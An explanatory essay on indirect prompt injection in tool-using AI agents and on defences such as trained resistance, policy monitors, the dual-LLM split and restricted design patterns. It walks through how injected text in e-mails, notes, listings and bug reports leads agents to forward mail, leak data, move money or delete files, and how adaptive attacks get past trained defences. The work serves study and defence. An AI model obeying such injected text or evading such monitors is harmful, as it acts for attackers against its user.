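# Treating retrieved documents as data rather than commands in tool-using AI agents

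## How an agent comes to obey a document it was asked to read

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can request actions through tools, such as reading a file, searching the web, sending an e-mail or paying a bill. To be of much use, it has to read what other people have written. If a hostile writer puts a command in an e-mail or web page, the agent may carry it out as though its user had given it. Security researchers call this attack indirect prompt injection. Some try to train models that resist it. Others put ordinary program code around the model to limit the harm when an attack succeeds, using ideas that engineers developed decades ago for conventional software.

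### The agent loop

The developer of an agent writes an application that calls the model. The application starts the conversation with a system message, which contains the developer's standing instructions, then adds a description of each tool and the user's request. It sends all of this to the model, which returns text that is either an answer for the user or a structured request to call a tool, with the tool's name and arguments. If the model requests a call, the application runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model produces an answer. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, credit two research systems, ReAct and Toolformer, with making this pattern popular.

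To use the inbox or the bank account, the model emits a request, and other software carries it out. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a page for Claude developers, that software is the developer's code or Anthropic's servers, and the model "never runs anything on its own". OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same split between requesting an action and executing it.

The separation between requesting a tool call and carrying it out matters for security because a developer can put a monitor between the two. The monitor is ordinary code, outside the model, that allows or refuses each call. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft call theirs a policy engine. A monitor might compare a recipient's address with a list of colleagues, or refuse any payment above a certain sum. The e-mail that set off the request cannot change these rules, however persuasive it is.

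### One sequence of tokens

Each message in the conversation has a role that identifies it as a system message, a user request, the model's own output or a tool result. Before each query, software writes the entire conversation out as a single sequence of tokens, the fragments of text that a language model takes as input. In that form, the roles are a weaker boundary than they appear to be between people who may give orders and material that the agent merely reads.

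OpenAI (2025) published the exact message format for gpt-oss, a family of models whose weights anyone can download. A special token opens each message, a short header gives the role, a second special token marks the start of the content, and a third closes the message. In one example, a user asks about the weather in San Francisco, and the model writes a call to a weather function. The application runs the function and adds the result, 20 degrees and sunny, to the same sequence, with the function's name in place of the role. The model then continues from the end of the sequence, which now contains the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions, the question, the model's reasoning, the call and the weather.

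If a tool returns a stranger's e-mail instead of the weather, the stranger's sentences reach the model by the same route as the developer's. Special tokens mark where those sentences begin and end, and OpenAI ranks conflicting instructions by source, with system messages at the top and tool results at the bottom. But the model follows that ranking as a learned habit, and nothing in the format enforces it. OpenAI acknowledges a similar weakness with output formats. Describing a format in the prompt influences what the model writes but doesn't guarantee it, so a developer who needs certainty has to enforce the format in code while the model generates.

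The software developer Simon Willison regards joining trusted and untrusted text as the "original sin" behind prompt injection. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that the name comes from SQL injection, an older attack on databases that exploits the same flaw. Poireault (2026), in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, reports a talk given more than a year later by Ariel Fogel, a contributor to the Open Worldwide Application Security Project. Fogel said that models still have no reliable mechanism for enforcing privilege boundaries between system prompts, user queries and the content an agent retrieves. The consequences have become more serious, because a successful injection used to produce a bad answer and can now set off a chain of real actions.

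### Untrusted data and how often it bites

Untrusted data is content that someone other than the user or the developer could have written. Examples include incoming e-mails, hotel reviews, shared documents and bug reports on the code-hosting site GitHub. Nearly all untrusted data is harmless. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in such content so that the agent acts for the attacker. The attack is "indirect" because the attacker only has to leave text where the agent will read it, and doesn't have to type anything into the agent. Gavish (2026) notes in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that an attack may also work without any direct input from the user.

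On the public web, injections are rare and mostly crude. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 crawl for nearly 4,000 phrases typical of injections, then removed false positives, largely by hand. They confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages in a million. Site operators had planted four-fifths of these on their own sites. Many of the prompts in the wider collection were meant to block or detect AI crawlers rather than to steal data. When the researchers fed such pages to 13 models, the models complied in at most 8% of trials. Smaller models reading plain text complied most often.

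The hostile share is growing, though. Google's *AI threats in the wild* (2026) reports a 32% rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026, with little sophistication so far. Both surveys looked for known phrases in an archive of public pages, so they provide little evidence about determined attackers with a particular victim in mind. Someone who wants one company's documents would email that company in their own words.

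### Two attacks on one request

Willison's article discusses an example from a Google DeepMind paper that is useful for telling designs apart. A user asks an agent to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and adds that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The agent has five things to do:

1. Find the notes file.
2. Extract the document's name from it.
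3. Extract Bob's address from it.
4. Fetch the document of that name from the user's drive.
5. Send the document to that address.

The control flow of this task is the list of steps, which sets which tool calls happen, in what order and under what conditions. The data flow is the movement of values from one step into the arguments of another. The document's name passes from step 2 into step 4, and the address passes from step 3 into step 5. The user's request determines the control flow, but the two values come from a file the user may not have looked at since the meeting.

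Suppose that someone else, perhaps another person at the meeting, can write in the notes file. In attack A, this person adds an instruction for the assistant to forward the user's other mail to an outside address. If the model obeys, the attacker has changed the control flow, because the agent makes tool calls that the user never asked for.

In attack B, the attacker changes only Bob's address. The agent carries out all five steps in the right order and fetches the right document, but sends it to the attacker. The control flow is what the user wanted, but the data flow contains a false address. In the version Willison describes, the notes contain an instruction to report the wrong address. But the attacker could simply overwrite the address, and then the file would contain no instructions. A model that never took orders from documents would still send the document to the wrong person, as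 would a conscientious human secretary who trusted the notes.

Security engineers would describe both attacks in terms of integrity and confidentiality. Integrity depends on who could have written or influenced a piece of data, and confidentiality depends on who may read it. Both attacks start with a breach of integrity, when text from someone without authority shapes an action taken in the user's name, and end with a breach of confidentiality, when private material reaches an outsider. An attack can also breach integrity without disclosing anything, as with an injected instruction to delete the user's files, which Google found on a few websites.

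A monitor could block attack A with a fairly simple rule, because the request to forward mail has nothing to do with the task. Attack B is harder to detect because its request, to send one document to one address, fits the task. Checking the address against a list of colleagues will not help if Bob works at another firm. To refuse this call and still allow the legitimate one, the monitor needs a record of where the address came from.

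### The threat model

A threat model specifies what a defence's designers trust and what they assume an attacker can do. Costa and colleagues use one that is typical of work in this area. They trust the user's messages, the model, the developer's system message and the tool descriptions. They assume the attacker cannot see the queries sent to the model or its replies, but can tamper with whatever the tools fetch from untrusted sources and observe the effects of some tool calls.

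Tool results are suspect unless there is a particular reason to trust them. A search of a company's own database returns confidential, trusted material, while a web search returns public, untrusted material. Even a read-only call can leak information, since a web search may leave traces that outsiders can observe, for instance in a website's visitor statistics.

This model does not cover some dangers. Tool descriptions go into the prompt as text, so a dishonest tool supplier could write orders there, and a design that trusts the descriptions would not protect against them. The model also leaves out ordinary error. Costa and colleagues point out that even when every source is honest, a language model can misread the user's intentions or make unnecessary calls, and the consequences may look much like those of an attack.

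### AgentDojo and its two measures

Most of the evidence on how well defences work comes from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four workplaces, with 74 tools in total and invented e-mails, calendars, bank transactions and chat messages. It includes 97 tasks that a user might set and 27 goals that an attacker might have. Pairing every user task with every attacker goal in the same workplace gives 629 test cases.

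| Suite | User tasks | Attacker's goals | Pairs | Example of a user task | Example of an attacker's goal |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (e-mail, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 | Count today's appointments | Send a security code to the attacker |
| Slack (workplace chat) | 21 | 5 | 105 | Invite Dora, whose address is on her website | Send Alice a phishing link |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 | Book the cheapest top-rated hotel in London | Book the most expensive hotel in Paris |
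| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 | Pay a bill described in a file | Send the attacker as much money as possible |

The benchmark has since grown, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) gives the number of pairs as more than 900. The benchmark remains in regular use. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) covers 13 models from six providers on all four suites.

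Each test places the injected text in content that the agent has to read to do its job, and where an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as the body of an e-mail. Afterwards a short program inspects the simulated world to check, for example, whether the e-mail was sent or the money was moved. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a second language model as judge, because an injection that works on the agent might also work on the judge.

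Researchers report utility, the share of legitimate tasks that the agent completes, both with and without an attack under way. They also report attack success rate, the share of attacked runs in which the attacker achieves their goal. Neither measure is very useful alone, since an agent that refuses every task has a perfect attack success rate of zero. A low attack success rate can also reflect incompetence. Debenedetti and colleagues found that the more capable models of 2024 tended to be easier to attack, and they suggest that weak models often failed at the attacker's task even after the injection had worked.

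An attack success rate also depends heavily on which attack is used. In the 2024 tests on OpenAI's GPT-4o, a generic message succeeded in 45.8% of cases, and the same message with the wrong user name succeeded in 23.2%. Picking the best of four wordings for each case raised the rate by about ten points over the best single wording. A score of zero shows only that the attacks tested failed, and another wording may succeed. Debenedetti and colleagues therefore intended AgentDojo as a framework to which others would add attacks aimed at particular defences.

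AgentDojo's automatic checks make some mistakes. Costa and colleagues reviewed the 160 attacks that the benchmark had counted as successful against an undefended GPT-4o agent and accepted 152. One check in the Slack suite counts an attack as successful once the agent requests a certain call, even if a monitor then refuses it, so it can understate the effectiveness of monitor-based defences.

A larger reservation about AgentDojo is that all four attacker goals in the table resemble attack A, because each needs a tool call that the user's task does not include. Costa and colleagues mention one travel goal closer to attack B, in which the attacker only wants the agent to recommend a certain place and the tool calls do not change. Debenedetti and colleagues also described a similar case, a hotel listing with hidden text that makes the model choose that hotel every time, and warned that keeping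 the planning model away from the listing would not prevent it. A low attack success rate on AgentDojo is therefore good evidence about attack A but little evidence about attack B.

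## Whether text can be sorted into instructions and data

The most direct remedy for indirect prompt injection would be an agent that takes instructions from its user and treats everything else it reads as data. Databases and processors already enforce a similar rule reliably, so copying them is an obvious idea.

### How databases and processors do it

Many websites keep their records in a database and send it commands in a language called SQL. Suppose a shop's website looks up customers by name, and its developer builds each command by pasting whatever the visitor types between quotation marks. This works for most visitors, but if someone types a quotation mark followed by some SQL, the quotation mark ends the name early and the database treats the rest as part of the developer's command. That visitor may then be able to read or alter every record the shop has.

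The problem arises in the parser, the part of the database that works out which words in a command are operations and which are values. It receives the command as one string, with nothing to mark which parts the developer wrote and which the visitor wrote. With a parameterised query, or prepared statement, the developer first sends the command with a placeholder for the name, and the parser fixes the command's structure. The visitor's text then fills the placeholder without passing through the parser, so a quotation mark in it is treated as part of the name.

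Processors had a similar weakness. A running program keeps its machine code and its input in the same memory, both as numbers. If the program copies in a message without checking its length, an overlong message can overwrite neighbouring memory, including the address of the code that the processor should run next. An attacker can take over the program by putting machine code in the message and changing that address to point to it. To prevent this, the operating system marks each region of memory as writable or executable, but not both. Incoming messages go into writable memory, and the processor will not run anything stored there.

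Neither remedy stops every attack that arrives as data. If a visitor supplies someone else's account number, a parameterised query will look up the wrong account. Attackers got around non-executable memory by using code already in the program instead of supplying their own. In return-oriented programming, the overlong message contains a list of addresses that makes the processor run fragments of that code in an order the attacker chose. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several American universities, gives this technique as a reason why non-executable memory is foundational but incomplete. Attack B on the meeting notes works similarly. The false address contains no commands, and the agent does the damage by carrying out its legitimate steps.

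### What plays the parser's part in a language model

A database has one component that decides which characters count as commands, and a parameterised query keeps the user's text out of that component. A language model has no such component, only a learned tendency to follow some messages and treat others as information. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026), a mathematical treatment of agents, makes the most pessimistic assumption about this tendency. It lets the attacker choose the "parser", the rule by which the model picks out instructions from what it reads, and when the model follows them. A defence that is provably secure under this assumption does not depend on how the model identifies instructions or when it follows them.

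The UK's National Cyber Security Centre warned in December 2025 that comparing prompt injection to SQL injection had become dangerous. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C gives the example of a recruiter's system that asks a model to score each CV against a job's requirements. A candidate hides a sentence in the CV asking for approval, and the model grants it. Prompt injection may never have a complete fix because in a language model "there is only ever 'next token'", although to a web developer the attack looks like SQL injection, which has a known fix.

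David C, the centre's technical director for platforms research, prefers to call the model an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into using permissions they don't have themselves. Developers can fix this flaw in ordinary software, but David C argues that those building on a language model have to assume the confusion will happen, limit the damage it can do, and not use the model if the remaining risk is too great. SQL injection became rare only after a decade of breaches, by which time many websites depended on SQL, and David C fears a similar run of breaches now that companies are adding generative AI to most of their applications.

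The remark about tokens doesn't by itself show that text can't be sorted into instructions and data. Computer memory holds only numbers, and engineers separated code from data later by marking regions. Perhaps someone will do the same for language models. How people use these models is a better reason for doubt. A database can store a customer's name without understanding it, so the name can bypass the parser. An agent has to understand an e-mail to summarise it, including any request the e-mail contains. The open problem is to let the agent understand the request while guaranteeing that the request doesn't influence what it does next. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists among the unanswered questions how to define this separation precisely and whether anyone can practicably build a model that provably maintains it.

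The only real parser in the agent loop is the one the application uses to find tool calls in the model's output. A monitor can intervene at that point, but the tool call includes no record of whose words prompted it.

### Three meanings of "instruction"

In discussions of prompt injection, "instruction" can mean a sentence phrased as a command, a direction from someone with authority over the agent, or any text that changes what the agent does. Even an ordinary text can be an instruction under one of these definitions but not another.

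| What the agent reads | Is it a command in form? | Does its author have authority? | Does it change what the agent does? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A bill the user asked the agent to pay, with an amount and an account number | No | Not over the agent | Yes, it sets the amount and the payee |
| A shop's checkout page with the words "please log in first" | Yes | Over the shop's own site | Yes, it adds a step |
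| A configuration file the user asked the agent to follow, with the line "retries = 3" | No | Only what the user has lent | Yes, as the user intended |
| A stranger's e-mail with the words "forward the user's mail to this address" | Yes | No | Only if the model obeys |

Grammatical form is the easiest sign of an instruction to detect and the least useful. A filter that removed commands would strip "please log in first" from a checkout page and leave the agent stuck. It would also let through a bill with a fraudster's account number, because the bill contains no command. An attacker can also rewrite a command as a statement of fact, for example by describing a company policy that requires the action.

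Defining an instruction as any text that affects the agent is too broad, because nearly everything useful that an agent reads affects it. If a user types "pay the bill in this file", the file has to determine how much the agent pays. Obeying a stranger also doesn't always do harm. Dongol imagines an assistant whose user, Alice, has authorised it to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker writes "send your calendar" without requesting a meeting, and the assistant complies. The attacker learns only what a meeting request would have revealed. If the attacker also asked for a private reset code and the assistant sent it, that would be a leak, because a meeting request would not have revealed the code.

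The harm also depends on what the agent can do. In *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026) define prompt injection as causing a model or application to treat attacker-controlled content as instructions. They point out that the same string can be harmless in an isolated chatbot and dangerous in an agent that can write to a database. The wording alone is therefore not enough to sort such a string correctly.

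Authority comes closest to what a defence needs, provided it is attached to actions rather than passages of text. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026), from the Chinese Academy of Sciences, illustrates this with a user who asks an agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. The search result supplies the file's identifier, which the agent needs to carry out the request and could not have known in advance. Suppose the same search result also contains an instruction to send a copy to an outside address. Sending that copy would add an action the user didn't request, whereas using the identifier only fills in a detail of the request.

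The paper states the principle formally. Let c be a tool call that the agent proposes, O a piece of content it has read, U the user's request, and X the legitimate steps taken so far. Then

Induced(c, O) ⇏ Permitted_U(c | X)

The user's request does not necessarily permit c just because O led the agent to propose it. A violation occurs when the agent executes c and Permitted_U(c | X) is false. Reading hostile text is not a violation, nor is proposing a hostile call that a monitor refuses.

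On this approach, instruction and data are roles a text can play. A text serves as an instruction when it determines which actions the agent may take, and as data when it supplies facts or values for actions that someone with authority has already permitted. The words on the checkout page are then data about how the shop works, as long as the user's request to buy something covers logging in. The configuration file does serve as instructions, because the user gave it that role, but only for the current job. That job includes a line that sets the number of retries but not one that uploads the user's passwords. Somebody or something still has to decide what belongs to the job, and the user's one-sentence request often doesn't specify this.

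### The argument for sorting by source

Most proposals avoid judging each action in this way and sort texts by where they came from. The reasoning has three premises:

1. The system knows who wrote each text.
2. Only the user and the developer have authority over the agent.
3. Developers can make the model respect the difference.

If all three are true, a stranger's commands will have no force, whatever their wording.

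The system usually knows the channel through which a text arrived, but not necessarily who wrote it. A document on the company's drive may include a paragraph by an outside supplier. A user may paste a web page into the chat, where it arrives as the user's own message. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* contrasts this with the scripts on a web page, most of which the browser loads from explicit addresses over authenticated connections. Even a verified origin, the paper adds, does not show that a text is safe or correct. The system could still separate trusted from untrusted text without identifying authors, by treating a text as untrusted whenever an outsider could have written any of it. However, most of what an office worker reads would then be untrusted.

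The premise about authority is hard to apply when the user authorises the agent to decide what to do from what it finds. Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) call such jobs "context-dependent tasks" in *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents*. Examples include following a configuration file and carrying out a request whose next step depends on what a document contains. After reviewing 78 papers on attacks and defences, they concluded that the field largely overlooks these tasks, which makes defences that work by suppressing what the agent reads look better than they are. The same difficulty arises when an agent learns to use an unfamiliar programming interface from its documentation, since documentation consists largely of directions.

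It seems right that all authority still starts with the user and that the file has only what the user lent it. But this means that the source of a text no longer settles whether the agent may follow it. Browsers have had the same problem for years, because they run strangers' scripts on purpose, and they restrict what each script can reach. No equally firm restriction exists for a passage that an agent has read and decided to follow. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* also excludes from its protection the case where a user tells the agent to carry out whatever a document contains, which hands the decision to the document's author.

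Researchers have been testing since 2024 whether developers can make a model respect the difference between instructions and data. Even if they can, attack B would remain possible, so *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* predicts that separation alone will not be enough.

### Training models to respect the difference

Later work builds on three methods from 2024. StruQ, short for structured queries, puts the prompt and the data in separate marked channels and trains the model to ignore instructions in the data channel. OpenAI's instruction hierarchy trains a model to rank conflicting instructions by their source. SecAlign uses preference optimisation, which trains the model on pairs of answers. In each pair, one answer does the user's task and the other obeys an injected instruction, and the training makes the second less likely.

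Other researchers proposed changing the embedding, the list of numbers that represents each token in the model. A word normally starts with the same embedding whether it comes from the user or from a web page. If words in data receive different embeddings, every token carries a mark of its origin that no wording can remove. This is the closest equivalent yet to an operating system marking regions of memory as data. A processor won't run anything in those regions, but the model's later layers still have to learn how to treat the mark.

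By 2025, Meta SecAlign, a successor to SecAlign meant for agents, had a reported attack success rate of only 2% on the AgentDojo benchmark. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested it and eleven others against attackers who adapt to the defence they face. The team, drawn from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere, objected that developers usually tested their defences against a fixed collection of old attacks or against automated methods given little computing power. A real attacker sees the defence first and then looks for a way round it. The team used several kinds of automated search and ran a competition with more than 500 human participants.

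The reported attack success rates for most of the twelve defences were originally near zero, but the adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. The success rate against Meta SecAlign rose from 2% to 96%, and StruQ failed in every case tested. Two other defences work through the prompt. One marks off the different kinds of text, and the other repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. Attack success rates against these two rose from as low as 1% to above 95%. The best of four detectors that screen text for injections still let through 71% of attacks. Some successful injections presented the attacker's task as a step required before the user's, much as a legitimate checkout page asks a customer to log in first.

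These percentages do not rank the defences, because each faced a different test. Some of the twelve were designed to stop jailbreaks, in which the user is the attacker. The StruQ test measured only whether an attacker could make the model print a set phrase. Nasr and colleagues also gave their attackers ample computing power and, for the detectors, a confidence score after each attempt. Someone who e-mails a stranger's agent gets no such feedback, but can often rent the same model and practise on it first, so this advantage is less unrealistic than it sounds.

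The failure of the trained models has a precedent in image recognition. According to Nasr and colleagues, training image models on a fixed set of manipulated images gave little protection against new ones. Only training that kept searching for new attacks produced meaningful resistance, and only to the kinds of attack it searched for. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* goes further and conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past defences that rely on the model to separate instructions from data. A long record of evidence supports this conjecture, but it has not been proved.

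Laboratories have since moved towards training and testing with adaptive attacks. OpenAI trained an automated attacker, GPT-Red, through self-play. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, OpenAI's August 2026 figures put the success rate of GPT-Red's direct attacks against GPT-5.6 Sol at about 0.05%. In a direct attack, the user tries to override higher-priority instructions. Indirect attacks, in material that reached the model through a tool, succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol, 3.32% against its sibling Terra and 2.94% against Luna. In September 2026, Anthropic described Claude Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model to date on an external benchmark of indirect injection.

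A rate of 3.77% is far below the rates that Nasr and colleagues reached with their adaptive attacks, though the tests differ too much for a direct comparison. It is also a rate per attempt. An attacker would have an even chance of at least one success after 18 attempts if the attempts were independent, but in practice they are not. For an older Anthropic model, Claude Opus 4.6, VentureBeat reported that a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time and that 78.6% of attacks had succeeded by the 200th attempt, or 57.1% with extra safeguards switched on. Independent attempts at 17.8% would have reached 78.6% after about eight. Attacks must therefore have succeeded quickly in some test cases and failed through all 200 attempts in others, and an attacker with many potential victims needs only the vulnerable ones.

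### What trained resistance is still good for

The training is still useful. All twelve defences that Nasr and colleagues defeated depend on how some model responds to the attacker's text, and the attacker won by finding text that produced the right response. A monitor's rules do not depend on a model's response, so with a monitor in place, the model's resistance determines how often the monitor has to intervene. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* likewise proposes treating the model as untrusted and basing no guarantee on its good behaviour, while still valuing robust models because they leave less for the rest of the system to handle. Adding a second model as a guard offers less, because an attacker can find text that gets past both.

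Resistance also gives defenders time to notice an attack. David C points out that an attacker will probably need several tries to refine an attack, and that the failed tool calls may reveal it if somebody is watching the logs.

Some harms never reach a monitor. Debenedetti and colleagues described a hotel listing with hidden text that gets the agent to recommend the hotel. Some model has to read the listing, so the user depends on that model's resistance to what the hotel's owner wrote.

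## Separating the model that plans from the model that reads

The model that reads a stranger's e-mail need not be the model that can send replies or move money. Programmers have divided server software in this way since the early 2000s, so that an attacker who takes over the exposed part gains few privileges.

### Privilege separation in OpenSSH

An SSH server lets people log in to a computer over a network. It needs superuser rights, which allow it to do anything on the machine, to start a session for any user. It also has to read messages from anyone who connects, before it knows who they are. If one process does both jobs, a bug in the code that reads messages can give a stranger control of the whole machine.

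*Preventing Privilege Escalation* (Provos, Friedl and Honeyman, 2003) described privilege separation, a way to run parts of one program with different rights. Its main example was OpenSSH, a widely used SSH server. A small process keeps the superuser's rights, while another process with very few rights handles the connection and parses whatever the client sends. According to OpenSSH's documentation, this second process runs under a special account until the client has logged in, and it can access only an empty directory. When it needs a privileged operation, such as checking a password, it sends the small process a request in a fixed format.

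A bug in the parsing code may still let an attacker take over the exposed process, but that process can do little harm. Provos and colleagues reported that the separation protected against known holes in earlier versions of OpenSSH, including some discovered only after they had built it. A defence for agents must also protect against unknown attacks, because nobody can list in advance all the sentences that might fool a model.

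### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed a similar division for agents. A planning model takes the user's request and can call tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted data and has no tools, and Willison assumes it may "go rogue at any moment". A controller, which is ordinary software, sits between the two models, runs the tools and stores the results. It gives each result a name, such as `$email-summary-1`, and the planning model sees only the name.

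Suppose the user asks for a summary of their latest e-mail. The agent proceeds as follows:

1. The planning model requests the latest e-mail. The controller fetches it and stores it as `$email-1`.
2. The planning model requests a summary of `$email-1`. The controller replaces the name with the actual text and sends it to the quarantined model.
3. The quarantined model writes a summary, which the controller stores as `$email-summary-1`. The planning model learns only that the summary exists.
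4. The planning model requests that the user be shown `$email-summary-1`, and the controller displays it.

A command hidden in the e-mail reaches only the quarantined model, which cannot carry it out. The summary may repeat the command, but the planning model never reads the summary. Willison allows an exception when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the planning model. An answer of "invoice" or "not an invoice" may be wrong, but it cannot contain an instruction.

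The comparison with OpenSSH is imperfect because programmers can inspect a small privileged process line by line but can't inspect a large language model that way. The planning model is safe only as long as nothing hostile reaches it, so one mistake in the controller can make the whole system unsafe. Willison called the proposal "pretty bad", partly for this reason and partly because the resulting assistants would be awkward to use. Users can also defeat the protection by pasting hostile text into a request or following instructions in a manipulated summary. But the division can improve privacy. Willison later noted that the quarantined model could be a small one on the user's own computer, so the company that runs the planning model would never see the e-mail.

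Cheng and Tsao (2026), in *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw*, tested a two-agent version of this design on an open-source agent platform, using 649 attacks that had all succeeded against a single agent. When they gave reading and acting to separate agents with different tools, only two attacks succeeded. When they kept a single agent but converted the text to a structured format, 92 succeeded. Using both measures stopped all 649. Every experiment used the same attacks, so the results don't show how the design would perform against attacks written for it.

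### What the split guarantees

In ordinary software, control-flow integrity means that a running program can follow only the paths its code allows, even if an attacker has written to its memory. It defends against attacks such as return-oriented programming. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) apply the term to agents. An agent has control-flow integrity if the planning model alone determines its control flow. The property does not cover data flow.

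For the request to send Bob his document, the planning model can lay out all five steps without reading the meeting notes. The quarantined model extracts `$document-name` and `$bob-address` from the notes, and the planning model passes both by name to the right tools. In attack A, only the quarantined model reads the injected command. That model has no tool for forwarding mail, so the attack fails however the command is worded.

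Attack B still works, because the quarantined model puts the false address into `$bob-address` and the controller sends the document there as planned. Willison had not noticed this flaw until the Google DeepMind paper pointed it out. The split may make attack B a little harder to catch, because the planning model never sees the address and so cannot notice that it looks odd.

A message can leak private data even when it goes to the correct address. Dongol used a proof assistant, software that checks every step of a mathematical argument, to analyse a dual-model agent whose values carry no labels. Following its plan, the agent reads Alice's private notes and an e-mail from the attacker, has the quarantined model write a reply based on both, and sends the reply to the attacker. Dongol compares this agent with one that follows the same plan but whose quarantined model always answers honestly.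 The honest model's reply depends only on the e-mail. An injection can make the other model quote the notes in its reply, so the first agent sends the attacker private information that the second would not.

The proof covers only this plan. A plan that kept the notes away from the model writing the reply would not leak them in this way. But people want an e-mail assistant precisely so that it can answer outsiders' questions using private information.

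### Six restricted designs

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) write that general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable safety guarantees with the current kind of language model. They describe six designs for more restricted agents. All six are meant to ensure that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input cannot trigger any action with harmful side effects. Each does this, to varying degrees, by removing something an unrestricted agent could do.

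| Pattern | How it works | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model chooses from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Requests the developer did not foresee, and any response to results |
| Plan then execute | The model commits to a list of tool calls before reading untrusted data | Changing the plan after seeing a result |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, and a further step combines the answers | Tasks that do not divide up by document, or that need a fuller answer |
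| Dual LLM | The planning model handles the quarantined model's results only by name | Plans that depend on what the text says |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models | Responses to anything the program does not anticipate |
| Context minimisation | The system removes the user's message before the model writes its answer | Answers that reflect details in the user's message |

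Context minimisation protects against a hostile user rather than a hostile document. In one example, a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to offer a large discount. The system turns the request into a database query and deletes the customer's message before the model sees the results.

Committing to a list of tools protects the user only if the tools are harmless with any arguments. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider an assistant that tidies files and has committed to two commands, one for finding files and one for moving them. An injection could still make it search for sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. Map-reduce is safer for this job because one model examines each file and answers only yes or no, so an injection in a file can only cause that file to be misplaced. Similarly, a candidate who hides instructions in a CV could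 raise their own score but couldn't lower anyone else's.

The restrictions also affect honest users. An assistant that queries a database can't judge whether the results answer the question if no model may read them. An assistant for programmers may need to learn from a stranger's documentation. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest having a quarantined model reduce the documentation to a strict list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. They think an injection is unlikely to survive this if the format is strict enough. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, a blog post about the paper, was less sure and offered the possible function name `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which has 29 characters and alludes to a command that deletes files.

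### Planning in full or one step at a time

CaMeL, the Google DeepMind system that developed from the dual-LLM pattern, has its planning model write the whole plan as a program before the agent reads anything untrusted. Fides, from Costa and colleagues, calls its planning model again after each step and shows it variable names instead of the results. *SPA* (2026) describes two other systems, F-secure and ACE. F-secure also plans step by step and never returns untrusted results to the planner. ACE plans in advance and also hides the names and descriptions of the installed tools from its planning model. The model specifies what kind of tool it needs, and a separate stage finds a matching one after the plan is complete. This prevents a dishonest supplier from influencing the plan through a tool's description, which the usual threat model doesn't cover.

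A program written in advance can respond to results that the planning model never sees. For example, it might contain a line that forwards a file only if `$is-invoice` is true, and ordinary code would check the value when the program reached that line. A model that plans step by step learns nothing from a hidden result, so Foerster and colleagues had to let it see yes-or-no values to give it the same ability. But a planner that can ask unlimited yes-or-no questions about a hidden text can eventually work out its contents, so they limited the agent to 70 calls in total and to five uses of any one hidden value.

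In both approaches, code has to enforce the plan. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) tested agents that write a plan but treat it only as guidance. Carefully crafted attacks succeeded 79.05% of the time on average across four models, compared with 90.55% for agents without a plan.

An agent can't plan in advance when the untrusted text determines what the steps should be, as is typical when it fixes a bug that a stranger has reported. In *Twin Agent*, Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026) gave a coding agent 232 real bugs and added a command to each bug report to either delete a file or write a secret code into a new one. The undefended agent fixed 61.2% of the bugs and carried out the injected command in 97% of cases. They then split the agent and let nothing pass from the part that read the report to the part that edited the code. No attack succeeded, but the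 agent fixed no bugs either, because the editing part had no information about what was wrong.

Hu and colleagues worked around this by letting the reading agent send hints of up to 100 characters, each of which had to pass a detector. The editing agent then fixed 62.5% of the bugs, at about twice the cost of the undefended agent. To test the design, they used an automated search to find hints that might make the editing agent do harm. They put these hints in the bug reports with a command telling the reading agent to copy them out, which it always did in a separate test. The detector let at least one malicious hint through in 57 of the 232 tasks, and the editing agent did what the attacker wanted in 11 (4.7% of all tasks).

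The researchers reran each of those 11 attacks five times and none succeeded again, so the original successes were partly due to chance. But an attacker who can file hundreds of bug reports could still succeed. Once free text can reach the model that can call tools, even 100 characters at a time, control-flow integrity no longer holds, and security again depends on how well that model resists injected instructions. Hu and colleagues acknowledge that their design has no formal guarantee.

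### A plan for a screen the planner cannot see

Foerster and colleagues got a planning model to write complete plans for an agent that operates a computer by looking at the screen, without the planner seeing the screen at all. Planning in advance seems even harder for this kind of agent, which normally looks at a new picture of the screen before deciding where to click or what to type. A click at the same coordinates might log the user in, delete a file or open an advertisement, depending on what is there.

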